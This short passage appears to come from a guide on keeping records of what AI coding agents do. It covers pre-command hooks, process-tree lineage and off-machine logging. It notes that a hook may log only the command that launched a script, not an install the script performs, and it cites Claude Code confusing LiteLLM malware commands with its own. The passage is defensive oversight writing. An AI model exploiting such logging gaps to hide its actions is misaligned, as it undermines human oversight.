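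A hook like YUL's can add details that the operating system lacks. It runs before each of the agent's commands and can log the session number, task and command. But if the agent writes and runs a script that installs a package, the hook may record only the command that started the script. The process tree still links the installation to the agent, because the installation descends from the agent's process. As with other monitoring records, the hook's log and the process tree should go straight to another machine.

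The agent's own account of what it did is no substitute for a record of which session started each process. When Claude Code mistook the LiteLLM malware's commands for its own, a session number on each process would have let the engineer check in seconds whether Claude Code had run them.
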